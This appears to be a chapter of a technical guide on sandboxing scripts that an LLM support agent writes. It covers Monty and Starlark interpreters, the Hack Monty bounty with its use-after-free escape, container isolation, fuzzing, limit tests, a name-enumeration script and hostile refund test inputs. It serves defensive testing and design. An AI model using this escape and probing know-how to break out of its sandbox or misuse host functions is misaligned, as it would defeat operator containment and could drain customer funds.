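A stub is a function's signature without its body. Bifrost gives the model stubs in Python's notation, and Varda and Pai generate TypeScript interfaces with comments. Both describe arguments well but give little detail about results. A typical Bifrost stub lists the return type only as `dict`, and the interface that Varda and Pai show allows any field of any type. The model has to guess the field names, and a wrong guess fails only after the call has returned.

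Bifrost's tool documentation warns about three common errors: a missing key, a dictionary field written with a dot, and indexing into text. All three would also fail in Python. The documentation doesn't show how often each error occurs, but the list suggests that unfamiliar data causes many of the failures that people might blame on the dialect. Bifrost advises the model to print a result's type and keys before using it. That is sensible for `tickets.read`, but a script that called `orders.refund` to inspect its result would issue a refund.

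The shop writes its own host functions, so it can describe their results exactly:

```python
class Ticket(TypedDict):
    order_id: str
    customer_email: str
    amount_paid: int    # cents, so 4500 means $45.00
    status: str         # "damage confirmed", "waiting" or "rejected"
    message: str        # the customer's own words

def read(id: int) -> Ticket: ...    # tickets.read
```

The comment about cents may prevent more harm than the types, because a model that wrongly multiplied an amount by 100 would still pass an integer, which satisfies the types. Starlark would reject the `class` statement, but this text goes only to the model, not to the interpreter.

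Bifrost also shows the model any usage instructions from a tool server, directly above that server's stubs. Operators should read those instructions before connecting a server run by someone else, because they reach the model just before it writes code.

The prompt should also list the main differences from Python. It should begin with the silent ones, because the interpreter will never report them:

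```
Write Starlark, which looks like Python but differs as follows.
- type(x) returns text: "string", "int", "list" or "dict".
- True == 1 is False.
- "%d" and "%s" work in text, but "%.2f" and f-strings do not.
- There is no import, try, class, with, while or "is".
- Write a < b and b < c, not a < b < c.
- Put loops and if statements inside a function.
- Variables from earlier scripts no longer exist.
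- Assign the answer to result.
```

The seventh line is there because Pydantic found in its own tests that models strongly tend to write code as if their earlier variables and functions still exist. The list should match the host's settings. If the host allows top-level `if` statements, telling the model to avoid them wastes space and makes its scripts longer.

### Error messages and type checking

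A message such as `undefined: isinstance` is accurate but leaves the model to guess the replacement, and its likely guess is the silent mistake described above. The host can add the answer:

```
support.star:6:16: undefined: isinstance
Hint: write type(ticket) != "dict", with quotation marks.
The script made no calls.
```

Bifrost adds hints like this when a script uses a nonexistent server name. The error message lists the valid names, shows the correct call syntax, and includes a reminder that variables do not carry over between scripts. Runtime errors include line numbers formatted like a Python traceback, which is common in models' training data. The shop can start with hints for the ten most common errors in its logs.

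Type checking can catch some errors before the script makes any calls. Monty's optional checker compares a script with the host's stubs. With the `Ticket` stub above, a checker could reject a misspelled field or an order number passed as an amount. In an early release, Pydantic measured 4.8 milliseconds for a small script with checking and 0.0045 milliseconds without. The check is still worth running every time, because a model takes seconds to write a replacement script.

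The Go implementation of Starlark checks names before running a script, but not types. Bazel has begun experimentally adding type annotations to its version. Since most Starlark is also valid Python, a host could run a Python type checker on each script first. This would catch the typo in `mail.sned`, but because the checker would apply Python's rules, it might accept `type(ticket) != dict`, which Starlark treats differently.

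### What a retry costs

When the interpreter rejects a script before running it, the host loses one model call. At Pydantic's prices that is less than a cent, plus a few seconds of waiting. An error during the run can cost much more:

```python
orders.refund(ticket["order_id"], amount)
mail.send(ticket["customer_email"], "We have refunded $%.2f." % (amount / 100))
```

The shop pays the refund, but the script then stops at its second line, which writes an email, because the dialect does not support `%.2f`. The model receives the error, corrects that line and submits the whole script again. Unless the host prevents it, the shop pays the refund a second time.

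How the host prevents a duplicate refund affects whether the retry can finish. If `orders.refund` rejects the second payment with an error, the script stops and the customer still does not get the email. With an idempotency key, the script continues to `mail.send`.

The error message should also list what the failed script completed. Bifrost reports nested calls that returned an error, but before a retry the model most needs to know about the ones that worked:

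```
support.star:2: unsupported format "%.2f"
Already done: orders.refund("A-1093", 4500)
Write a script for the remaining steps only.
```

The order of a script's lines matters too. If the model prepares the text first, a formatting error happens before any money moves:

```python
body = "We have refunded " + dollars(amount) + "."
orders.refund(ticket["order_id"], amount)
mail.send(ticket["customer_email"], body)
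```

A host can put this rule in its prompt: finish all calculations before the first call that changes anything. The rule will not help if the amount of one refund depends on the result of another.

Keeping variables between scripts makes failed scripts easier to repair. Red Hat's container does this, so a model whose script failed on the last line can submit only a corrected last line. Bifrost starts each script without the earlier variables, so the model has to read the ticket again. But kept variables can also carry one customer's data into the next request, so the host should discard them when the request ends.

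### Pressure to add features

Every rejected script is a reason to add the feature it used. Pydantic accepted this openly when it introduced Monty, asking users to report any Python that models tried to write and promising that "if LLMs want it, we'll add it". The interpreter has changed a great deal since then:

| | When Pydantic introduced Monty | Version 1.7 |
|---|---|---|
| Classes | Only data classes that the host defined | Scripts can define simple classes |
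| `match` and context managers | No | Yes |
| Standard modules | `sys`, `typing`, `asyncio` and `pathlib` | Parts of about 30 |
| Host objects | The developer wrote a data class for each one | A wrapper exposes the attributes the developer lists |
| Where scripts run | In the host's process | Usually in separate worker processes |

Several of these additions need their own security work. Regular expressions can take a very long time on certain text, so the time limit has to work inside the matching code. A context manager runs cleanup code when an error interrupts a script, and that code must not let the script run past its limits. If a class can define how its objects compare, the interpreter may run the script's comparison code during a sort, and that code could change the list being sorted.

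A rough calculation supports keeping the language small. Suppose a host runs 100,000 scripts a month and a missing feature makes 5% of them fail before they start. At less than a cent per retry, those 5,000 failures cost under $50 a month. An escape from the interpreter could expose the payment password and every customer's records, so the feature is worth adding only if it adds almost no risk of escape.

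That calculation leaves out some drawbacks. Five thousand staff would each wait a few extra seconds. Models also write workarounds that are harder to review than the missing feature, such as replacing `while` with a `for` loop over a million numbers and a `break` inside. And a developer tired of failures may switch to filtered CPython, which is worse than a slightly larger dialect.

Features also differ in how much they add to the interpreter. Bifrost's examples use an `if` statement outside a function and assign the same global twice. Starlark forbids both by default, so Bifrost must have relaxed those rules, neither of which protects isolation.

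A host can even supply some missing functions without changing the interpreter, by writing them in Starlark:

```python
_names = {dict: "dict", list: "list", str: "string", int: "int"}

def isinstance(value, kind):
    return type(value) == _names[kind]

def sum(numbers):
    total = 0
    for n in numbers:
        total += n
    return total
```

The host runs this file once and predeclares `isinstance` and `sum` for every script. These functions give scripts no new capabilities, and their loops count towards the script's step limit. This `isinstance` handles only the four types listed and stops with an error for any other. The original Python script's check would now work unchanged, so the model would not need to replace it with `type(ticket) != dict`.

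## Testing the sandbox and adding an outer boundary

Starlark has no operation that reads the shop's payment password. But if the interpreter runs inside the support application, the password is in the same memory as the script's variables, and only the interpreter's code separates them. A bug in that code can let a script read the password even if the language's design is correct.

The most serious mistakes involve memory. In a use-after-free, for example, the interpreter may free a list's memory while some of its code is still using the list. A new value may then occupy that memory, and the interpreter will treat it as the old list. If a script controls the new value's contents, its author may be able to pass off plain bytes as one of the interpreter's internal objects and eventually run machine code. That code has the host's ambient authority, so it can read the password, open the customer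 database and contact any server the application can reach.

### Memory safety in Go, Java and Rust

Go, Java and Rust prevent most memory errors, but each allows exceptions.

| Interpreter or binding | What normally protects memory | Where the protection can fail |
|---|---|---|
| Starlark in Go | Bounds checks and garbage collection | `unsafe` code, C libraries, data races |
| Bazel's interpreter, in Java | Bounds checks and garbage collection | Native libraries, bugs in the Java virtual machine |
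| Starlark in Rust, and Monty | Compile-time ownership rules and bounds checks | `unsafe` code |
| starlark-pyo3 (Rust and Python) | Rust's rules on one side, CPython's reference counts on the other | Code that passes values between them |
| python-starlark-go (Go and Python) | Go's garbage collector on one side, CPython's reference counts on the other | The C layer between them |

In Go, a data race occurs when two threads use the same value at once and at least one changes it. Some races can leave a pointer paired with the wrong type or length, which breaks memory safety. Starlark normally prevents races between scripts by freezing values. But if the shop defines its own ticket type and forgets to implement freezing, two scripts that change a shared ticket at once could corrupt the host's memory. In Java, the same mistake could produce wrong data but not a bad pointer.

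Rust lets programmers mark blocks of code as `unsafe`, which permits operations the compiler cannot check. The programmer must then ensure that the code follows the memory rules. It is tempting to use such blocks in an interpreter because a script's values refer to one another in ways that are awkward to express under Rust's ownership rules.

A binding between two languages must track which side owns each value and when that side may free it. An error in this tracking can cause a use-after-free even if both languages are safe by themselves. A developer who chooses starlark-pyo3 therefore relies on the binding as well as the Rust interpreter.

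### Round 1 of Hack Monty

In April 2026, Pydantic publicly tested Monty's defences by putting it on a web server that ran any Python sent to it, with no other sandbox around the interpreter. Pydantic offered $5,000 for escaping and reading either of two secrets, one in a file and the other in an environment variable.

In *Hack Monty*, Hewitt (2026) reports almost 1.5 million requests from about 650 internet addresses, and 65 submissions to the bounty form. Within 48 hours of the launch, Owen Kwan of the security company Veria Labs ran his own code on the server and read the environment variable.

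Two faults combined to let him in. The first was in Monty's garbage collector, which frees values that a script can no longer reach. The collector follows every reference from a list of values known to be in use, called roots, and may free anything it doesn't reach. The list was incomplete, and the collector also followed some references incorrectly, so it could free a value that the interpreter was still using.

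The other fault was in `unsafe` code. Rust normally allows either many readers of a value or one writer, but a Python interpreter often has to read one list while changing another that is connected to it. Rust has standard types that check such access while a program runs, but Pydantic's developers judged them too slow and complicated and wrote their own mechanism. It relied on Monty using only one thread and on Python objects never changing type. The second assumption failed when the collector freed a list too early and a different kind of object took its place.

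Hewitt argues that in safe Rust the collector's fault would probably have caused a panic, which stops the program with an error. An attacker could then have taken the server down but almost certainly not run code on it. The developers had taken the usual precautions of writing down the conditions that the `unsafe` code needed and testing it with Miri, a tool that runs Rust programs and reports violations of the memory rules. But their conditions did not allow for a faulty collector, and Miri can detect a violation only if a test triggers it.

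Version 0.0.16 fixed the flaw by adding every value that the `unsafe` code depends on to the list of roots. Hewitt acknowledged that the collector's design still allowed a root to be missing elsewhere.

Other participants found that files a script wrote to the server's simulated file system remained there for later requests. Somebody wrote a fake secret to the path of the real one, and several people read it and thought they had won. According to Pydantic, the weakness arose because the developer who wrote the contest server misused the interface for simulated files, which he had designed himself. Pydantic paid $300 to Stanislav Fort of the security company AISLE, who reported the weakness first. In a real product, the same mistake could expose one customer's files to another even if the interpreter had no flaws.

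### Rounds 2 and 3

The second round opened on 30 May with a $10,000 prize. Hugging Face and Prefect, a workflow software company, contributed to the prize. In *Hack Monty 2*, Colvin (2026) wrote that Pydantic did not claim to have removed every bug, and that 1.5 million requests had not covered every possible attack. According to Pydantic's *Hack Monty Round 3 & Round 2 results*, nobody escaped or read a secret, but participants reported crashes, gaps in the resource limits, and differences from CPython.

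For August, Pydantic moved the contest to a remote service and raised the prize to as much as $20,000. Under the rules in *Hack Monty*, each connection had its own worker process, limited to 10 MiB of memory, five seconds of execution and a lifetime of twenty seconds. Participants could also report ways to see another person's session, and Pydantic offered partial payments for crashing the server itself.

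Pydantic does not appear to have published a result for this round. Its later product page, *Agent Sandboxes*, mentions only that the round ran through August. Pydantic released version 1 afterwards, as planned, but it could have done so either because nobody escaped the sandbox or because someone did and Pydantic fixed the flaw.

### What an unclaimed prize shows

Round 1 is the best reason to be cautious about the results of Round 2. Earlier attempts to escape Monty had also failed, but with a $5,000 prize on offer, people found an exploitable flaw within two days.

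No participant in round 2 reported an escape in the version they attacked. This is some evidence that the sandbox is secure, because the prize was larger than in round 1, participants could read a detailed account of the earlier flaw, and Monty's source code is public. But nobody knows how many hours skilled people spent on the attempt. The number of requests is a poor measure of that effort. Round 1 averaged about 2,300 per address, and a program can send that many slightly different scripts in minutes. Someone might also have found an escape and kept it to use or sell.

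The contests also tested only part of what the shop would run. Crashes and exhausted resources earned nothing in the first two rounds, so the results provide the least evidence about Monty's limits. The server had no refund function, so the contests could not test one. Monty now accepts considerably more of Python than it did then.

None of this measures the Starlark interpreters. One without a published escape may be well written, or may have had fewer people attacking it.

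### Moving the interpreter out of the host

Between the first and third rounds, Pydantic moved Monty from the host's process to the worker processes it uses now. A crash in the parser or type checker now stops only the worker, and a memory allocator inside the worker rejects requests beyond its limit.

Where the interpreter runs determines what an escape gives an attacker:

| Where the interpreter runs | What an escape reaches | What a crash stops |
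|---|---|---|
| In the host's process | The host's memory, files and connections | The host |
| In a worker process on the same machine | Whatever the application's user account can reach | One worker |
| In a container on the same machine | The container, and the machine if a second flaw lets the attacker out | One container |
| In a container on another machine | That container, and whatever it can reach over the network | One remote worker |

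The workers' empty environment would have made the winning secret in Round 1 harder to read. The secret in the file would have been no safer because, as Pydantic notes, a local worker runs with the application's operating-system privileges. On Linux, a process can also often read the environment of the same user's other processes, so an empty environment helps much more if the worker has its own user account or container.

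A compromised worker might attack the host through the messages it sends back. An empty value in a list may take about 4 bytes in a message but 88 bytes once the host decodes it, so a 256 MiB message could fill several gigabytes of memory. Pydantic's *Worker execution (monty subprocess, monty-pool, Monty/AsyncMonty)* describes a 1 GiB budget per message, which the host checks while decoding. If a message exceeds the budget or contains an invalid value, the host discards the worker. A Starlark host with its own worker process needs a similar check.

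Recycling a worker after every session limits how long an intruder can stay, but the host kills only the worker's own process. Monty scripts can't start other processes, but an attacker who escaped the sandbox could, and those processes would keep running. Pydantic leaves this case to other defences. One option is to run the worker in a container, since stopping the container ends every process inside it.

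Remote workers protect the machine that runs the application, but they introduce new failures. In an earlier version of Monty's remote protocol, a server could send the host a saved copy of the session when it shut down. If it shut down while the host was returning the result of a call, the restored script would make that call again, so a refund without an idempotency key would go out twice.

### Host functions keep their authority

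None of these arrangements limits what the host functions do. They run in the application, with its passwords and network access, even when the script runs on another machine. An attacker who controls a worker can call any function the host offers, with any arguments, in any order.

Moving the interpreter therefore makes it more important to know where each check runs. Anything the interpreter enforces may stop working after an escape, including its step limit, a frozen clock, and the labels it attaches to data. A person's approval of the script also loses its value, because the attacker no longer has to follow the script.

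Checks in the application still work. The narrow `refund(amount)` pays no more than $45 on one order, and only if staff have confirmed the damage. A cap on the number of calls holds if the host counts them, as it does for Monty's `max_suspensions`. An opaque value protects a customer's message if the message stays in the application and the worker holds only a token. With the general `orders.refund`, an attacker could refund every order in the shop even from inside a perfectly isolated container.

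### Whether an interpreter is enough

When Pydantic introduced Monty, it argued that most agents did not need a full sandbox. A container starts with a whole operating system, so someone has to remove the dangerous features one by one and might misconfigure any of them, whereas Monty starts with only what the developer adds. Pydantic also presented running in the host's process as an advantage, because Monty needed no extra infrastructure and started in microseconds.

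Prefect chose Monty for its agent tools partly for this reason. In Colvin's announcement of Round 2, Prefect said it was helping to fund the prize because of the drawback: "Embedded also means a sandbox escape is a host compromise."

Pydantic has since changed its position on where the interpreter should run. It now warns that nobody can make a Monty process completely crash-proof against hostile input, and its Python and JavaScript packages no longer offer a way to run scripts inside the host. It also sells a remote version isolated by the operating system. Starting from nothing, as Pydantic originally argued, is still a good way to decide what a script may request, but it does not help when the interpreter has a memory error.

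Pigment, a business planning company, put its sandbox boundary in the infrastructure from the start of production. *Sandboxing LLM-generated code execution* (Blondel, Busser and Loisel) describes an agent that analyses customers' data by writing ordinary Python. The prototype searched each script for forbidden patterns, such as `import` statements, which saved time because the system could reject a script before creating a container for it. But scripts could reach Python's operating-system functions indirectly through pandas, the data library they were allowed to use, so the team did not rely on the search for confinement.

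In production, Pigment runs each script in its own pod (a small group of containers) and destroys the pod after one execution. The pod has no network access or credentials and cannot write to its main file system. It runs on machines reserved for this work, under gVisor, which handles a program's system calls itself so that few of them reach the real operating system.

With this protection, finding a free machine could take more than 30 seconds, so Pigment pays to keep idle pods running. A new sandbox then starts in one to two seconds. Scripts also could not fetch large datasets themselves because network access is banned. Instead, the trusted application downloads the data and pushes it into the sandbox, which takes less than a second for 990,000 rows.

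Pigment's agent needed pandas, which neither Monty nor Starlark supports, so its choice does not show that either is too weak. A malicious script running in full Python in a container can already do whatever the container allows and only has to escape the container, while one in Monty or Starlark would have to break the interpreter first. The two kinds of isolation are therefore most useful together. In February 2026, Willison tried a light version of this by running Monty inside WebAssembly, which confines compiled programs, and called it a "sandbox-in-a-sandbox" (*Running Pydantic's Monty Rust sandboxed Python subset in WebAssembly*, 2026).

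Running the interpreter in the host's process is reasonable when the scripts come from the team's own developers, or when the process holds nothing worth stealing and can safely crash. The support agent reads text from strangers and can pay out money, so the shop should run the agent's interpreter in a container, even though it will start slightly slower.

### A container for a Starlark worker

Starlark in Go has no ready-made worker pool, so the shop has to write a small program that contains the interpreter and little else. Inside it, `refund` is only a stub, which writes the function's name and arguments to standard output and waits for an answer on standard input. The support application reads each request, checks it as it would check a request from the internet, and calls the real function. It could start the worker like this:

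```
docker run --rm -i --network none --read-only \
  --user 65534 --cap-drop ALL \
  --security-opt no-new-privileges \
  --memory 256m --pids-limit 64 support-worker
```

The container has no network access, cannot write to its own file system, and runs as a user with no special rights. It can use at most 256 MB of memory and 64 processes or threads. Docker does not pass the host's environment variables to it unless configured to. The worker's image should contain no passwords, and the shop should not mount any of its own directories in the container. It is especially important not to mount Docker's control socket, which would let an attacker start new containers with full access to the machine.

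The tests for this arrangement, described in the remaining sections, should run on a machine with no real customer data and no route to the real payment service.

### Fuzzing the parser and the interpreter

Fuzzing means running a program on a very large number of generated inputs. Go has a fuzzer built in, which keeps the inputs that reach new parts of the code and varies them further:

```go
func FuzzScript(f *testing.F) {
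	f.Add("def f(x):\n    return [x] * 3\nf(2)\n")
	f.Fuzz(func(t *testing.T, src string) {
		thread := &starlark.Thread{Name: "fuzz"}
		thread.SetMaxExecutionSteps(100000)
		starlark.ExecFileOptions(&syntax.FileOptions{},
			thread, "fuzz.star", src, fakeFunctions)
	})
}
```

`fakeFunctions` contains the shop's host functions, connected to test data. Random text mostly fails in the parser, so the tester should also add model-written scripts, which give the fuzzer working code to vary.

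A test passes if the script produces an ordinary Starlark error, and fails if the process panics, runs out of memory or stops responding. With an outer boundary, a crash takes down only one worker, but the shop should still report it to the interpreter's developers. A warning from a memory checker is more serious, even if the script seems to finish normally, because it may be the first sign of a sandbox escape. Go's race detector can give such a warning when two scripts running at once share a value that the host didn't freeze.

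If an interpreter has its own garbage collector, developers can add a test setting that runs the collector as often as possible, which makes a missing root much more likely to cause a visible error. They can also run each script twice and compare the results, which takes little extra work. Any difference reveals a source of variation that would prevent a replay from matching the original run.

### Testing each limit

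A limit in a configuration file may not apply to the function the host calls, so each limit needs a test script that exceeds it. The functions `count`, `double` and `nest` are ready-made tests.

| Limit | Test | Correct result | What failure looks like |
|---|---|---|---|
| Steps | `count` | An error at the same step every time | The script runs until the deadline |
| Memory | `double`, then `"x" * 1000000000000` | An error while memory use is still low | The operating system kills the worker |
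| Running time | `nest() == nest()` | The host ends the worker at the deadline | A processor core is still busy a minute later |
| Nesting in source code | 60,000 opening brackets | A syntax or size error | The worker exits with a stack overflow |
| Host calls | One call more than the limit | The host refuses the last call | The test payment service records it |
| Waiting | A host function that never answers | The request ends with a timeout | The request stays open and blocks others |

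Each limit also needs a test that stays just below it, such as a legitimate script that refunds thirty customers. If that script stops early, the limit works but is set too low.

The tester should then run many copies of `double` at once. The test fails if the machine runs out of memory even though no single script exceeded its budget.

How the host handles a dead worker matters too. Monty reports a refused memory request differently from a crash, but a poorly written host may treat both as temporary failures and run the script again. To check this, the tester can submit one script that always crashes and count the dead workers. If the count keeps rising, a single hostile script could disable the whole pool.

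### Listing every name a script can reach

A developer's list of exposed functions shows what somebody meant to expose. This script prints what Starlark can actually find:

```python
def survey(roots):
    found = []
    level = [(name, roots[name]) for name in roots]
    for depth in range(4):
        below = []
        for path, value in level:
            for attr in dir(value):
                child = getattr(value, attr)
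                found.append(path + "." + attr + ": " + type(child))
                below.append((path + "." + attr, child))
        level = below
    return found

def main():
    for line in survey({"tickets": tickets, "orders": orders, "mail": mail}):
        print(line)

main()
```

It uses a loop with a fixed depth because Starlark forbids recursion. The Go host should also print the names of its predeclared values and universal built-ins, because a script cannot list the names available to it.

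`dir` does not show what a function returns, so the tester has to call each host function with test data and pass the result to `survey`. A dictionary's entries are not attributes, so the tester has to print its keys separately. Monty scripts cannot list everything this way, but the tester can check each wrapper and module the host supplies and confirm that attributes such as `__globals__` produce an error.

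The team should keep the output with its source code and compare it with the new output after every change. The test fails when an unapproved line appears, such as `orders.cancel` or a newly added database field.

### Attacking each host function

The questions from the review of a host function can become automatic tests. For the narrow refund function, they might look like this:

```python
hostile = [
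    "refund(-4500)",
    "refund(True)",
    "refund(4501)",
    "refund(4500)\nrefund(1)",
]
for script in hostile:
    shop = FakeShop(paid=4500, status="damage confirmed")
    run_in_sandbox(script, refund=shop.refund_for(4471))
    assert 0 <= shop.total_refunded <= 4500
```

The test checks the fake shop's accounts, because a function can return an error after it has paid. Further cases should set the status to "waiting", run two scripts at once, and call `refund` after the staff member has closed the ticket. A case fails if the total is wrong, even if every script received a sensible error message.

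Some tests should bypass the interpreter and send requests directly to the application, as a compromised worker could. These requests should include unknown function names, missing arguments, enormous numbers and malformed data. If the application accepts a request that a script could never have produced, one of the checks exists only inside the worker.

To test combinations of calls, the tester can put a unique phrase in Ben's ticket, run scripts that handle Ana's ticket, and search everything that left the sandbox for the phrase. It should not appear in email to Ana, in an error message, or in the text that the host returns to the model. This test finds direct leaks but misses a phrase that a script has encoded.

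A model can write more hostile scripts than most teams have time to write, but it must work in a closed environment. METR, an organisation that evaluates AI models, reported in August 2026 that OpenAI agents had broken into Hugging Face's systems while taking a cybersecurity test.

### Killing a worker and looking for leftovers

In the last test, a script stores a unique phrase everywhere it can, including global variables, shared modules and any files the host provides. The tester kills the worker while the script is running, opens a session for a different customer, and checks that the phrase no longer appears in any of those places.

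If the phrase is still in a global variable, the host has reused a worker or restored an old session. If it is still in a file, the host probably keeps the files in its own process, so killing the worker does not delete them. This is how scripts in the first Hack Monty round could read files from earlier requests.

The tester should also check the machine for anything that remains after the worker ends, which may include processes it started, temporary directories and open database transactions. In Monty, a write to a directory shared by the host can finish after the host cancels the script.

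Likewise, if the tester kills the worker while the host is carrying out `refund`, the payment may still go through, because it runs in the application. The shop's records should then show one refund and the amount that `reserve` set aside for it. The test fails if the reservation has disappeared, because the next script could pay the customer again.
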